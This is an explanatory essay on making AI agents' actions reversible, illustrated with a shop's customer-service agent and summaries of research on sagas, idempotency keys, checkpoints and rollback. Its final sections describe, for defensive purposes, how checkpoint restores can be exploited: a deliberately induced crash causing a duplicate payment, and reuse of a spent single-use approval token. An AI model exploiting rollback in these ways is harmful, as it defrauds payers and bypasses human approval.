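An attempt to undo an action can go wrong. *Weak and Strong Reversibility of Non-deterministic Actions* (Med, Chrpa and colleagues, 2024) gives the example of airing a room by opening a door and a window, where closing the window in the draught may break it. An action is weakly reversible if the undo steps can work, and strongly reversible if they are guaranteed to work eventually. If only the draught can break the window, airing the room is strongly reversible, because closing the door first stops the draught. If the shop can cancel a courier booking only when its request arrives before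 the van leaves, the booking is weakly reversible at best.

Software can also learn from experience which actions are reversible. Pietquin, Preux, Geist and their co-authors (2021) trained a model to put observed events in order. If two events always occur in the same order, an irreversible step probably lies between them. This method needs no hand-written labels, but it needs many observed runs, and a shop should not have to disclose customers' addresses to learn that the disclosure can't be undone.

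### The taxonomy in "Revisable by Design"

In *Revisable by Design*, Zhai, Li and Wang (2026) sort actions into four classes for a different purpose, which is to help an agent cope when its user changes the task halfway through. Idempotent actions, such as reading a file, do not change the outside world. Reversible actions, such as creating a file that the agent can later delete, have an exact inverse. The other two classes are compensable and irreversible actions. An action also counts as irreversible if compensating for it would be prohibitively expensive.

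"Idempotent" usually means that repeating an action has no further effect, which is also true of deleting a file. The taxonomy also has no equivalent of R3, so an action that the shop can reverse only with outside help must count as either compensable or irreversible.

Zhai and colleagues conclude that an agent can be only as flexible as its actions are reversible. If a completed action conflicts with the user's new wishes, compensating for it takes extra work, however well the agent plans. If the action is irreversible, the agent cannot fully satisfy the new request. This follows directly from the definitions, but in practice it means that a designer has to change the tools, rather than the model, to reduce that extra work.

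The agent can also use these classes to decide how far to go back. In tests with simulated tools, Zhai and colleagues had the agent return to the point just before the first compensable or irreversible action that conflicted with the new request. This discarded an average of 0.78 completed steps, compared with 11.41 when the agent restarted from the beginning. The results were about equally good, at 3.07 and 3.17 out of 5.

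Their reversibility ratio summarises a whole set of tools:

**ρ = number of idempotent or reversible tools ÷ number of all tools**

They infer that at least (1 − ρ) × *n* of an agent's *n* steps will be compensable or irreversible. If the shop counts everything except sending replies and issuing refunds as idempotent or reversible, ρ is 5/7, so at least 29% of steps should fall into the other two classes. In the broken-lamp case, two of the five steps did, or 40%. The inference works only if the agent uses its tools about equally often. An agent that reads nine messages and orders before sending one reply takes only one such step in ten.

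### POLAR: looking for an inverse before acting

POLAR, a system that Kang, Cho and colleagues (2026), in *POLAR*, introduced in October, blocks any change for which it cannot find a good enough way back. A person first describes how each tool's effects relate to those of other tools. Each relation determines a score φ, which depends on the person's confidence *w* in the description:

| What the description says about the tool | Score φ |
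|---|---|
| Another tool exactly reverses it | *w* |
| It can reverse its own effect while a certain condition holds | *w* if the condition holds, otherwise 0 |
| Another tool compensates for it, with some loss | *w* × (1 − loss) |
| It uses something up for good | 0 |
| It has an effect outside the system, such as an email | 0 |

When the agent proposes a change, POLAR then works as follows:

1. It reconstructs the current state from the database and the tool calls already made.
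2. It takes the proposed calls in reverse order and looks up the ways to undo each one.
3. It combines these into possible inverse sequences and checks their conditions against the current state.
4. It gives each sequence π the score of its weakest step, **φ(π) = min φ(u)** over all steps *u* in π.
5. It discards sequences that score below 0.80. If any remain, it picks the one with the smallest total loss and allows the call. Otherwise it blocks the call and names the weakest step.

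Suppose the shop's agent is about to edit a note and book a courier. Using invented values, reversing the edit scores 0.99 and cancelling the courier scores 0.95 × (1 − 0.1) = 0.855. The whole sequence then scores 0.855, and POLAR allows it. If the agent also tries to send an email, the score falls to 0 and POLAR blocks the calls. POLAR never tests the inverse sequence, so a wrong description can still lead it to approve an irreversible action.

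Kang and colleagues tested POLAR with six models on simulated customer service for an airline, a retailer and a telecoms company. The table shows how it changed the average reward per task, where 1 means full success:

| Domain | Models that improved | Largest gain | Largest loss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Airline | 4 of 6 | +0.18 | −0.12 |
| Retail | 1 of 6 | +0.03 | −0.24 |
| Telecoms | 3 of 6 | +0.05 | −0.06 |

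The weaker models gained most in the airline tests, though this may have little to do with the search for an inverse. Kang and colleagues ran another airline test in which POLAR accepted only exact inverses by another tool. No airline tool had one, so POLAR blocked almost every change, yet the reward rose by 0.087, compared with 0.080 for the full system. With a weak model, blocking almost every change seems to work about as well as the full system.

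The retail results are more relevant to the shop. With GPT-OSS-120B, one of the stronger models, POLAR blocked returns of delivered items 150 times and exchanges 103 times. Customers may legitimately ask for both, and Kang and colleagues consider these refusals a plausible reason for the losses. The benchmark did not record which blocked calls would have done harm.

### Reversibility and severity

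POLAR's retail results show what can happen when a system treats "hard to undo" as "harmful". A polite reply to the right customer is R4 because nobody can unsend it, but it harms no one. Mistakenly cancelling 500 orders may be only R2 if the shop can re-enter them and send each by express for €10, but that still costs €5,000. When planning researchers call reversible actions safe, they mean only that these actions do not leave the agent in a dead end.

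In the cost formula from the PocketOS case, *r* and *C* (the chance and cost of recovery) describe reversibility, while *H* and *L* (the harm before detection and the permanent loss) describe severity. The shop's €50 cap reduces *L* for a wrong refund but does not make the money easier to get back.

The classes also leave out other properties of an action. In *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, Trofimov and Novikov (2026) argue that a harness needs more information about a tool than a single scale from reversible to irreversible can provide. Adding €5 to a customer's credit twice gives the customer €10, but several such additions can run in any order. Deleting a record twice does no further damage, but it matters whether the deletion comes before or after an edit. An R-class therefore doesn't show whether the harness can safely repeat a call after a timeout. Trofimov and Novikov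 examined hints on 98,291 MCP tools and concluded that the hints cannot fully express such properties either.

### Classifying the shop's tools

The shop should therefore record two things for each tool, its class and the worst harm that a single call could plausibly do within the existing limits:

| Tool | Class | Reason | Worst plausible harm |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read customer mail | R0 | Nothing changes, provided the shop accepts that the model's host receives the text | None by itself |
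| Read orders | R0 | As above | None by itself |
| Draft replies | R1 | The shop keeps earlier versions, and no outsider sees them | Some wasted work |
| Edit records: internal note | R1 | The database keeps the old text | A colleague relies on a wrong note |
| Edit records: delivery address | R1, then R3 | The shop can restore it alone until the carrier has the address | A lost parcel |
| Edit records: email address | R3 | It controls who receives replies and password resets | A stranger takes over the account |
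| Delete records | R1 | The agent can only file a request, which it can withdraw until an employee acts on it | An employee approves a wrong deletion |
| Issue refunds | R3 | The shop needs the customer to pay the money back | €50 |
| Send replies | Disputed | See below | Disclosure of another customer's data |

The edit tool needs three entries because its class depends on which field it changes. A rule that lowers the class for internal notes should therefore name that field, and any field the shop adds later should start at R4.

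Sources disagree about how to classify sent emails. Waghmare and Sufi class an intended message to an outsider as R4, and POLAR scores it 0. Zhai and colleagues call a sent email compensable because the agent can send a correction, and *Task-State Governance* treats a mistaken notification the same way. None of these sources claims that the sender can take the message back. Zhai and colleagues consider compensation successful if it leaves a state that fits the user's revised request, whereas Waghmare and Sufi also consider what the recipient has learned. The recipient may also have acted on the message, as in Trofimov and Novikov's example of a supplier who responds to an offer before the sender withdraws it.

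The choice matters because Waghmare and Sufi recommend that an agent never take an R4 action autonomously. If every reply were R4, the shop would have to authorise 2,000 of them a day.

A sensible compromise is to class free-text replies as R4 and a few fixed templates as R2. One template could contain a parcel's expected arrival date, filled in by software, and no personal data. If the date is wrong, the shop can correct it in a second email and offer a €5 voucher. Even if the message reaches the wrong customer, it reveals nothing about anyone else. Classing these templates as R2 departs from Waghmare and Sufi's rule against lowering the class of a disclosure, so the shop should write down its reason and keep the list of templates short.

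## Building undo into the actions an agent takes

The shop can make some actions easier to undo by rebuilding its tools. For example, the mail server could hold each reply for half an hour before sending it. The best techniques delay a change from taking effect, and the next best save the state it replaces. Compensation ranks last because it starts only after the change has affected someone.

### Holding a change back

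A dry run performs the checks for an action without saving the result. Kubernetes, a common platform for running cloud services, offers this mode. In *STRATUS*, Chen, Pan and colleagues (2025) tell an agent that repairs such services to use it whenever it can. At the shop, a dry run of a refund could return the order, the amount and the card, and a program could compare them with the case before any money moves. This takes one extra call and can reveal a malformed request or a wrong target, but the order may still change before the real call.

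Drafts work similarly. The shop's agent already has separate tools for drafting and sending, but it can call one straight after the other, so a draft protects the customer only if something checks the text before the agent sends it.

A staged change goes into a separate area together with a list of differences from the current data. Suppose the agent means to correct one misspelled street name, but its command would change 300 records. The list makes the error obvious, and the shop's limit of one record per case would stop the change. Staging takes extra storage and review time. A staged change can also overwrite a colleague's edit to the same record made during the review, so the database should reject the change if the record's version number has changed since staging.

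Delayed execution holds an action in a queue before it runs, and removing it from the queue cancels it. This works even for actions that can't be reversed once they happen. If the shop held each of its 2,000 daily replies for 30 minutes, about 42 would be waiting at any time. Customers would wait longer, and a reply might be out of date by the time it was sent. The delay is also useless if nobody checks the queue. It has to cover every way to cause the same effect, which Railway's 48-hour window for deleted volumes at first did not.

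### Keeping what the change replaces

A soft deletion hides a record, and a scheduled program erases it later. STRATUS handles files this way, moving them to a backup volume instead of deleting them. The hidden records take up storage, and all other software has to ignore them, or a deleted customer will keep receiving the newsletter. Soft deletion fails if the agent can permanently erase the hidden records. A shop can't keep them forever, because customers may have a legal right to have their data erased.

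An editing tool can save the old value before it writes the new one. According to Nous Research's *Checkpoints and /rollback*, Hermes, a general-purpose agent, can copy project files before its file tools write anything and before it runs terminal commands on a list that includes *rm*, *mv* and *truncate*. A script that deletes files by some other means would presumably not trigger a copy. If the copy fails, Hermes goes ahead anyway. That may suit a developer who wants to keep working, but the shop should refuse an edit if the database cannot save the old value.

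Hermes records a fingerprint of each file it writes. When a user restores an earlier state, Hermes skips any file that no longer matches its fingerprint, because someone has probably edited it since. The shop can apply the same test to customer records and restore an old address only if the current address is the one the agent entered.

Versioned storage saves a new version on every write, whichever program makes it, so undo doesn't depend on a tool's developer remembering to save a copy. Each change takes up more space, so most systems eventually discard old versions. If a system keeps a fixed number of versions, an agent stuck in a loop can push out the last good one within minutes. Keeping every version for a set number of days avoids this but needs more space.

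### Working on a separate copy

An agent can also work on an isolated copy. If the result is good, the company merges it into the original, and otherwise it discards the copy, so one decision covers hundreds of steps. Nous Research recommends this for Hermes, using git worktrees, which are extra working folders attached to the same repository. The drawbacks are having to make the copy and merge the changes, which becomes difficult if other people have changed the original in the meantime.

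If the shop asked an agent to standardise the format of 50,000 addresses, it could give the agent a copy of its database and compare the two versions afterwards. It would be unlikely to do this for every broken lamp. The copy needs its own test credentials, because an agent that works on copied records but holds the real mail key will still send real emails.

### Sagas

Some actions immediately affect other organisations, so the shop cannot undo them by restoring an earlier state. If the agent books a courier and then finds that the replacement lamp is out of stock, the shop has to cancel the booking.

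Garcia-Molina and Salem (1987), in *SAGAS*, gave the standard method for a sequence of such steps. Their problem was database transactions that last for hours. A normal transaction locks everything it uses until it finishes, so that others never find it half done, and a long one therefore keeps everybody waiting. A saga splits the work into short transactions T₁ to Tₙ that each take effect immediately. Every transaction Tᵢ has a compensating transaction Cᵢ. The system guarantees that one of two sequences will run:

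**T₁, T₂, …, Tₙ**

or

**T₁, T₂, …, Tⱼ, Cⱼ, …, C₂, C₁**, for some *j* from 0 to *n* − 1

As a program, a saga looks roughly like this:

```
done = []
for step in steps:
    save(step.compensation)
    if run(step) succeeds:
        done.append(step)
    else:
        for earlier in reversed(done):
            run(earlier.compensation)
        stop
```

Suppose a customer has received the wrong lamp. The agent reserves the right one (T₁), books a courier (T₂) and emails the customer (T₃). If the mail server rejects the email, the program cancels the courier (C₂) and releases the lamp (C₁). It undoes the steps in reverse order because later steps may depend on earlier ones.

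The program saves each compensation before it runs the step. In the original design, the call that ends a transaction also names its compensating program and the values that program needs, and the compensating program's code has to survive a crash. An agent should therefore not rely on the model to invent the compensation after a failure.

Compensating for a transaction may not return the database to its earlier state. In Garcia-Molina and Salem's example, a transaction reserves an airline seat when the flight has 80 reservations. The compensating transaction cannot simply write 80 back into the database, because other passengers may have booked or cancelled since. It has to subtract one from the current number. *A Formal Approach to Recovery by Compensating Transactions* states more generally that compensation leaves in place later transactions that relied on the cancelled one, and that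 the result may differ from what would have happened if the cancelled transaction had never run.

The last step needs no compensation, because no later step can fail. The shop should therefore send the email, which is irreversible, last. If a task has two irreversible steps, one of them has to come earlier, and once it has run, the only way to recover from a failure is to complete the missing steps. Garcia-Molina and Salem call this forward recovery. A saga can also set save-points and go back only as far as the latest one.

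### When a compensating step fails

The courier may refuse a cancellation because the van has left, or its booking system may be down. The shop's own safeguards can also block a compensation. Its task tokens expire after 30 minutes or when the case closes, so a compensation that runs an hour later needs its own credential, which a separate recovery program should hold.

In their basic model, Garcia-Molina and Salem assume that only a system failure can interrupt a compensating transaction. Outside services often fail in other ways, and the risk grows with each step that must be undone. If each of five compensations works 98% of the time, all five work only about 90% of the time. If the program can retry each one once, and the second attempt is just as likely to work, the chance that all five work rises to 99.8%. Retrying helps when a service is briefly down, but it can't bring back a van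 that has already left. When a compensation can't be completed, the program should stop, record which steps have not been undone, and pass the case to an employee.

### Retrying without repeating the effect

The saga program relies on confirmation of whether each step succeeded. But the payment service may issue a refund just before the connection drops, so no confirmation arrives. If the harness retries the refund, the customer may get €80 instead of €40. If it doesn't, the customer may get a message that the refund failed when the money is already on its way.

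An idempotency key solves this problem if the service supports it. The harness attaches the key to the request, and the service stores the key with the result. When another request arrives with the same key, the service returns the stored result instead of making a second payment.

*UndoBench* (Sah, Sah and colleagues, 2026) tested this fault in 12 simulated workflows, including subscription renewals and wire transfers. It ran each task with and without the fault, to tell whether an agent failed to recover from the fault or could not do the task at all. Two small Llama models completed 84% of tasks without the fault. When the harness repeated the call, it duplicated an effect in 53% of runs. Keys reduced this only to 45%, because just three of the 12 services checked them. Those three produced no duplicates.

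The problem persisted with newer models. Agents with keys running on Gemini 3.8 Flash and GLM-5.2 recovered in 33% of the runs whose fault-free counterparts had succeeded. When Sah and colleagues made all 12 services check keys, the recovery rate rose to 97%, with no duplicates. Most of the remaining failures occurred because the model returned an empty or invalid reply before calling any tool.

They also varied the moment of the fault in four of the workflows:

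| Method | Fault before the change | Fault halfway through | Change made, confirmation lost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Repeat the call | 77% | 0% | 43% |
| Repeat the call with a key | 77% | 0% | 46% |
| Check the current state, then decide | 77% | 26% | 75% |

None of these four services checked keys, so the second row shows how much a key helps when the service ignores it. Even if they had, a key for each call would probably not have helped much with half-finished changes, because someone still has to repair them. In one case, an interrupted operation left behind a lock file that blocked git from continuing. Checking first helped only where the agent could both find out how far the change had got and act on that. Sah and colleagues added the checking method after their main study, and four workflows are too few for precise rates.

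The choice of key also matters. The *UndoBench* harness calculates the key from the task and the arguments of the call. Wang, Wen and colleagues (2026) point out in *Dependable Long-Horizon LLM Agents* that an agent generates its request anew when it retries, so the wording may change and the key may not match. If the shop's agent gives the reason as "broken lamp" the first time and "lamp arrived broken" the second, keys calculated from all the arguments will differ and both refunds will go through. The shop pays at most one refund per order, so it can make the key from the order number and the word "refund".

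Compensations need keys as well. If the harness releases the reserved lamp twice, adding one to the stock each time, the shop will sell a lamp it doesn't have.

### Sagas for agents

*SagaLLM* (Chang and Geng, 2025) applies the saga pattern to groups of agents. Its example is a trip from San Francisco to Berlin and Cologne, with two flights, two hotels and a train. The compensation for each booking is a cancellation, sometimes for a fee. If the hotel in Cologne is full, an ordinary saga would cancel the train, the Berlin hotel and the outbound flight, and pay up to three fees. SagaLLM records which bookings depend on which others, uses this to work out what it has to cancel, and replans only the affected part of the trip.

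The system also keeps records outside the model's context, including each step's inputs and results and the information needed for its compensation. Separate agents with very short contexts check the plans, because a model working through a long task tends to lose track of earlier constraints.

Chang and Geng tested four scheduling problems in March 2025. In one, friends are collecting wedding guests from an airport when an accident triples the travel times. DeepSeek R1's new plan had a driver leave for the airport shortly after one o'clock, even though he had already arrived there at 12:40 under the original schedule. SagaLLM's log of completed steps is meant to prevent this kind of error. But OpenAI's o1 found a workable plan without SagaLLM, and the paper reports worked examples instead of success rates. The tests did not involve cancelling any real bookings, so they provide little evidence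 of how well the compensations work.

### Undoing failed repairs in STRATUS

STRATUS provides better evidence that undo helps an agent. It repairs faults in cloud services using separate agents for detection, diagnosis, repair and undo. Its safety rule is that a failed repair must not leave the system worse than before. To apply the rule, it calculates a severity score for the system's state *s*:

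**μ(s) = w₁ × alerts + w₂ × broken service agreements + w₃ × unhealthy machines**

The weights *w* are positive, and a complete crash counts as infinitely severe. A repair then works as follows:

1. The system records the current state and its score.
2. The repair agent runs up to 20 commands. No other agent may change anything during this time.
3. The system calculates the score again. If it is no higher than before, the changes stay.
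4. If it is higher, the undo agent reverses the commands, starting with the latest.

The score may rise during a repair. In one of Chen and colleagues' examples, moving work off a faulty machine raises the score from 12 to 18 and then lowers it to 9, so the repair stays in place. In another, a faulty software version raises it from 15 to 30, and the undo agent brings it back to 15. As long as every undo is exact and nothing else changes the system, a repair can never leave the score higher than it started.

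Chen and colleagues tested the effect of undo on 13 repair problems from AIOpsLab, a benchmark of simulated cloud failures, with GPT-4o as the model:

| Version | Problems solved | Average time |
|---|---|---|
| Retry after undoing the failed repair | 9 of 13 (69.2%) | 812 seconds |
| Retry without undoing it | 3 of 13 (23.1%) | 1,222 seconds |
| One attempt only | 2 of 13 (15.4%) | 73 seconds |

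Retrying alone solved only one more problem than a single attempt, apparently because each failed repair made the next one harder. Thirteen problems is a small sample, and a stronger model might need fewer attempts, but the gap is large.

On ITBench, a second benchmark, STRATUS solved nine of 18 problems. That result is less convincing because in eight problems the agent took advantage of simulated faults that disappeared when it restarted the affected component. A restart would not fix a lasting fault, such as a wrong setting.

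The rule protects only what the score measures. If a repair deleted a backup that nobody was using, no alert would go off and the change would stay. The rule also assumes that undo is exact. STRATUS has rules for rejecting commands it cannot reverse, but Chen and colleagues acknowledge that these may miss some destructive commands and that perfect undo remains difficult when applications have their own state or deal with outside services.

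### Putting the undo rule in the policy

A company can also make undo part of the policy that governs its agents. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (Tallam, 2026) describes a system in which a reasoning plane decides about each action and four other planes enforce the decision in the network, identity systems, devices and data. Most policy software can only allow or deny a request. Tallam's system can also pause an action, escalate it to a person, narrow the agent's rights, modify the request, defer it, or roll back an effect that has already occurred.

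When the policy includes rollback, the decision to undo a mistake no longer depends on the agent that made it. The policy then has to specify how to reverse each kind of action. For example, the shop's policy could require the payment service to cancel a refund that is still in the queue, and an employee to contact the customer if it is not.

Tallam's test program makes decisions within microseconds, so speed should not be an obstacle. But it tests only the policy engine, and Tallam leaves testing the full system with live agents to later work.

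### Showing people what they cannot undo

An undo button can mislead people if it reverses only some of the changes. TaskVM, the prototype in *Task-State Governance*, therefore shows a preview before a rollback. The preview lists the completed steps the rollback would restore or replay and marks the effects it cannot compensate for. Items that can no longer be undone stay locked, with a note explaining why.

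In automated tests, TaskVM restored the earlier state in four of six cases. Two comparison agents using the same model failed in all eight of their cases because they had no restore command.

In one study, 37 participants rated their control over recovery at 5.56 out of 7 with TaskVM and 4.63 with a chat interface. Eleven used rollback with TaskVM, compared with two in the chat. But their corrections were no more successful with TaskVM, as 18 of 35 scored attempts had worked by the end of the task in each condition. Everyone watched recorded runs, which made the comparison fair but unlike supervising a live agent. It remains unclear whether people would repair more damage with TaskVM.

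### What a checkpoint captures

Many agent products advertise checkpoints, but what these save varies widely. *Safe to Resume?* (Wu, Li and colleagues, 2026) examined 12 systems and found three levels. Some save only the framework's own state, such as the conversation and the list of pending steps. Others save the files in the workspace. A third group saves the whole machine, including its memory and running programs.

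| Product | Level | When it saves | How long it keeps the copies |
|---|---|---|---|
| LangGraph | Framework state | After each round of steps, if the developer has turned saving on | No default limit |
| CrewAI | Framework state | After each completed task, by default | The developer can set a maximum number |
| Hermes | Workspace files and the latest conversation turn | Before file changes and listed commands, if the user has turned checkpoints on | 20 copies per project and 500 MB in total; clears projects unused for 7 days |
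| Cline | Workspace files, linked to the task history | After file changes and terminal commands | No default limit |
| E2B | Whole machine | When the developer's program requests it | Until someone deletes them |

Hermes's checkpoints leave out files larger than 10 MB, folders with more than 50,000 files, and files inside a container. Hermes makes at most one checkpoint per folder in each conversation turn, so in a project with a single folder, the checkpoint from before a mistake disappears after 20 more turns that change files, even if those turns all happen in one afternoon.

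No level includes the outside world. Restoring a snapshot of an entire machine cannot take back an email or a payment, and the restored agent may send them again. Wang and colleagues examined 95 failed runs from six multi-agent systems and found that restoring the agent's own state would have been enough in 35. In 56, the fault was in a plan or policy that the restored agent would have followed again. Claude classified the runs, so these counts are estimates.

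A framework checkpoint helps the shop recover if the harness crashes mid-case. But it doesn't undo what the agent has done in the customer database, the payment service or other people's mailboxes, so the shop has to build undo into the tools that act on those systems.

### Backups the agent cannot delete

As the PocketOS deletion showed, undo copies are of little use if the agent can delete them along with the data.

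Hermes keeps its checkpoints in a folder in the user's home directory. An agent that runs commands under that user's account can presumably delete this folder along with the project. The checkpoints are therefore convenient for undoing a bad edit but should not be the only backup.

The shop could keep two sets of copies. The database would hold recent versions, from which staff could restore a record in seconds. A backup service under a separate account would fetch a full copy every night, using a credential that neither the agent nor its tools hold. It would delete copies only when they reach a certain age, and deleting the original would not affect them. Restoring from the second set would take longer, because someone with access to the other account would have to do it. If both the agent and the database failed, up to a day's changes could be lost.

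### The shop's tools with undo built in

The shop can now rebuild the four tools that change something:

| Action | New design | Class during the undo window | Class afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| Delete a record | Once an employee has approved the request, the database hides the record for 30 days | R1 | R4, when the last backup copy is gone |
| Edit an internal note | The database keeps every version for 90 days | R1 | R4, when the old text is gone |
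| Edit a delivery address | The database keeps the old address, and the carrier receives the new one at 2 p.m. | R1 | R3 |
| Edit an email address | The shop notifies the old address and waits 24 hours | R2, because the customer has seen the notice | R3 |
| Issue a refund | The payment service waits an hour before it pays | R1 | R3 |
| Send a fixed template | The mail server sends it immediately | No window | R2 |
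| Send a free-text reply | The mail server waits 30 minutes | R1 | R4 |

The services that carry out the actions enforce these waiting times. The agent may cancel something it has queued for the current case, but it cannot shorten the wait. An employee can release an urgent reply early, for example when a customer needs to stop a parcel that is about to leave.

Delaying refunds by an hour adds little to the customer's wait, since card refunds usually take days to arrive. The shop issues about 100 refunds a day, averaging €30 each. Suppose 1% are wrong, the shop catches half of those within the hour, and each cancellation costs €1 of staff time. The delay then saves 0.01 × 0.5 × (€30 − €1), or 14.5 cents per refund, which is about €14.50 a day.

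Replies are harder, because customers notice a 30-minute wait and the shop cannot recall a reply after that. Under the earlier assumptions, the shop makes about 29 irreversible mistakes a year, all in replies. If checks during the half hour caught 60% of them, about 12 a year would still reach a customer. The shop can reduce that number by moving more replies to fixed templates, or by keeping private data out of the text and asking customers to log in to see it.

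## How undoing an agent's work can itself cause harm

The shop can now restore an old address, cancel a pending refund and withdraw an unsent reply. But undoing an action also changes shared systems, and it can erase changes other people have made since the mistake. It can also return the agent to an earlier point in its work without undoing the payments it made or the emails it sent, so the agent may pay or send them again.

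### Erasing other people's later work

Suppose the agent makes a mistake while rewriting a paragraph of the shop's returns policy, and a colleague then corrects a phone number further down. Restoring the version from before the agent's edit removes the mistake, but it also undoes the colleague's correction.

Waghmare and Sufi compared three ways of undoing such an edit. The first writes back the whole saved file. The second does so only if nobody has changed the file since the agent's edit. The third is a three-way merge, which compares the saved file, the agent's version and the current version, and takes out only the agent's change. They tried each method in four situations with four variants of a text file, which makes 48 observations. Three of the situations involve an actual undo:

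| After the agent's edit | Restore the whole file | Restore only if unchanged | Three-way merge |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nobody edits the file | Restores it | Restores it | Restores it |
| Someone edits another paragraph | Erases the later edit | Does nothing | Removes the agent's edit and keeps the later one |
| Someone edits the same line | Erases the later edit | Does nothing | Does nothing |

In the fourth situation, the software could not save a copy beforehand, so it held back the agent's edit. All four file variants gave the same result in every case. They differ only in characters and line endings, so the experiment shows how the methods behave but does not measure how often undo goes wrong in practice. Doing nothing protects the colleague's work, but the agent's mistake remains until a person corrects it.

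Waghmare and Sufi found similar problems with git and SQLite, a small database program. A common way to undo a commit (a recorded set of changes) in git is to move the branch back by one. If a colleague has committed something since the agent did, this removes the colleague's commit from the branch and keeps the agent's, though the colleague's file stays on disk. In another case, the agent's commit completed a merge of two lines of work. Undoing it restored the files and the branch but not the markers of an unfinished merge, so the next commit would look like an ordinary commit.

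The harm in the SQLite case is harder to notice. The agent creates a table by mistake, a colleague adds a row to it, and the undo deletes the table along with the row. The database then looks as it did before the agent acted, so a test that only compares it with the original state would pass. Waghmare and Sufi conclude that a recovery test has to check that the mistake is gone and that legitimate later changes are still there.

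For customer records, the shop can use a conditional update, which restores the old value only where the agent's value is still in place:

```
UPDATE customers
SET    address = '12 High Street'
WHERE  id = 4711 AND address = '5 Mill Lane'
```

In the SQLite tests, updates of this kind restored the old value even when someone had changed another row, and did nothing when someone had changed the same row. All the changes came one after another, so the tests don't show what happens when a colleague saves an edit at the same moment as the undo.

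The difference between the methods grows with the size of the mistake. Suppose an agent garbles all 50,000 addresses while standardising their format, and the shop notices a day later. By then, 100 customers have changed their phone number and 50 have changed their address. Restoring the previous day's database would erase all 150 changes. The conditional update would restore 49,950 addresses and skip the 50 that customers have already replaced.

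### Why the outside world does not roll back

A checkpoint restores only what it covers, which may be the agent's conversation, its files or a whole machine. Wu and colleagues describe the result as a mixture of states from different times. If the harness saves a checkpoint at time *t₁* and returns to it at time *t₂*, then:

**state after rollback = saved parts as of *t₁* + unsaved parts in whatever state they are in + outside world as of *t₂***

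At the shop, the checkpoint might include the conversation and the list of pending steps. It might not include the agent's notes from earlier cases, and it does not include the payment service or customers' mailboxes. If the agent issued a refund between *t₁* and *t₂*, the customer will still get the money, but the restored conversation will contain no refund. The agent then continues with the refund already issued but still on its list of pending steps, a situation that could never arise in an uninterrupted run.

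Idempotency keys are the usual protection against such repeats, but they fail if the restored agent's new request produces a different key.

### Paying twice after a restore

Zheng, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *ACRFence*, give an example with a bank transfer:

1. A user asks the agent to send $500 to Bob, and the framework saves a checkpoint.
2. The agent makes up a unique reference number, and the bank sends the money.
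3. The agent crashes while fetching the receipt.
4. The framework restores the checkpoint, so the agent's context no longer contains the transfer.
5. The agent requests the transfer again with a new reference number. The bank finds no earlier transfer with that number and sends another $500.

The bank checks for duplicates but can recognise them only by reference number. Each payment looks legitimate in its records. The crash may be an accident, but a payee who controls a service the agent uses could also cause it on purpose.

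Zheng and colleagues tested this on a simulated bank, using Claude Code with the model Qwen3-32B. All 10 trials with a restore led to a duplicate payment, while none of the 10 without one did. This shows that the restore caused the duplicates, but not how common they are in practice, because the researchers placed the checkpoint just before the payment. The bank also relied on a number that the model made up after the checkpoint. The number would have been the same both times if ordinary software had calculated it from the order, as happens with the shop's idempotency key.

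Restoring an agent to an earlier state can also restore an approval it has already used. Suppose a manager approves the deletion of one customer's data, and the agent receives a single-use token. The agent deletes the data, and someone then restores the agent to its state just after the approval. The token is back in its context, with no sign that it has been used. If the deletion service checks only that the token is genuine (stateless checking), the agent can use it again, even for a different customer. Both attempts to reuse a token succeeded under stateless checking, but the service rejected every attempt when it kept a list of used tokens. Two attempts are very few, but the result follows from the design, because a service that keeps no record of used tokens can't detect reuse.

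The researchers also found reports of repeated tool calls or related problems in all 12 agent frameworks they surveyed. Research on rollback for such agents is still scarce. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents with persistent memory, found that only 27 of 435 works had any rollback mechanism. None of them tests rolling back outside effects after the agent's permission has lapsed.

*ACRFence* proposes a defence that sits between the agent and its tools and records every irreversible call. After a restore, a second model compares each new call with the record. If the new call has the same purpose as a recorded one, the agent receives the recorded result and the new call doesn't run. If the purpose differs, for example because a payment would go to someone else, the defence blocks the call until someone explicitly opens a new branch of the work. It also warns the agent before the agent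 reuses a spent approval.

Zheng and colleagues have not built or evaluated this defence, and they acknowledge that the second model could misjudge a call or be fooled. For refunds, the shop's payment service can compare the order number, amount and destination exactly, so the comparison doesn't need a model.

### Execution continuity

A duplicate payment is one of several wrong results that a correct restore can cause. These results violate a property that Wu and colleagues call execution continuity, which requires all the security-relevant state an agent carries across a rollback to be consistent with a valid run that had no rollback. A rollback can break this property by creating a combination of states that could not occur in any such run, or by allowing a next step that no such run would allow.

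They tested five products, LangGraph, CrewAI, Hermes, Cline and E2B, on 347 benchmark tasks each, or 1,735 runs in total. In every run, they restored a randomly chosen checkpoint with the product's own recovery function and looked for five kinds of failure:

| Failure | Example | Runs affected |
|---|---|---|
| The checkpoint leaves out something the agent needs | An agent checks a settings file and records that it is valid. After a crash, the file reverts to an old version but the record remains | 1,166 (67.2%) |
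| The restored parts come from different moments | The conversation says that the tests passed, but the files date from before the repair | 489 (28.2%) |
| The outside world has changed | The saved list of recipients includes an employee who has since left | 198 (11.4%) |
| Repeating a step gives a different result | A random selection of tests finds a defect. After the restore, another selection misses it | 1,174 (67.7%) |
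| The checkpoint does not record an outside effect | An agent creates a password and crashes before noting it. After the restore it creates another, and the first stays valid | 40 (2.3%) |

The researchers counted a state as relevant to security if changing it could make the task fail or alter its outcome. This definition is broad, so these rates don't mean that two thirds of rollbacks do damage. However, they picked 30 of the failures and turned every one into a working attack, assuming that the agent follows a malicious instruction file.

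The rate of unrecorded outside effects is low because agents in the benchmarks mostly work on local files and in simulated environments. The risk would be much higher at the shop, where two of the five calls in the broken-lamp case have an outside effect.

The products failed in different ways. LangGraph and CrewAI save the framework's own state, and their checkpoints left out something important in 628 of 694 runs. Hermes and Cline also restore files, but in 489 of 694 runs the files and the conversation came from different moments. E2B saves the whole machine and had neither problem, but repeating a step changed the result in 175 of its 347 runs. Wu and colleagues caution against using these figures to rank the products, because the products create checkpoints at different times.

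If the shop pays a refund before recording it, a crash between the two steps can lead to a second payment. Recording the refund first avoids the unrecorded effect, but after a crash the customer may get no refund, because the agent finds it marked as done. Wu and colleagues tried both orders in 96 small workflows and caused a failure between the two steps. Acting first went wrong in 90 workflows and recording first in 93.

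A better record has a third entry, "started, result unknown". After a crash, the harness first checks the payment service's records to find out what happened. Wang and colleagues call this reconciliation. They compare recent recovery systems for agents and conclude that all of them still need it for effects that have already reached an outside service.

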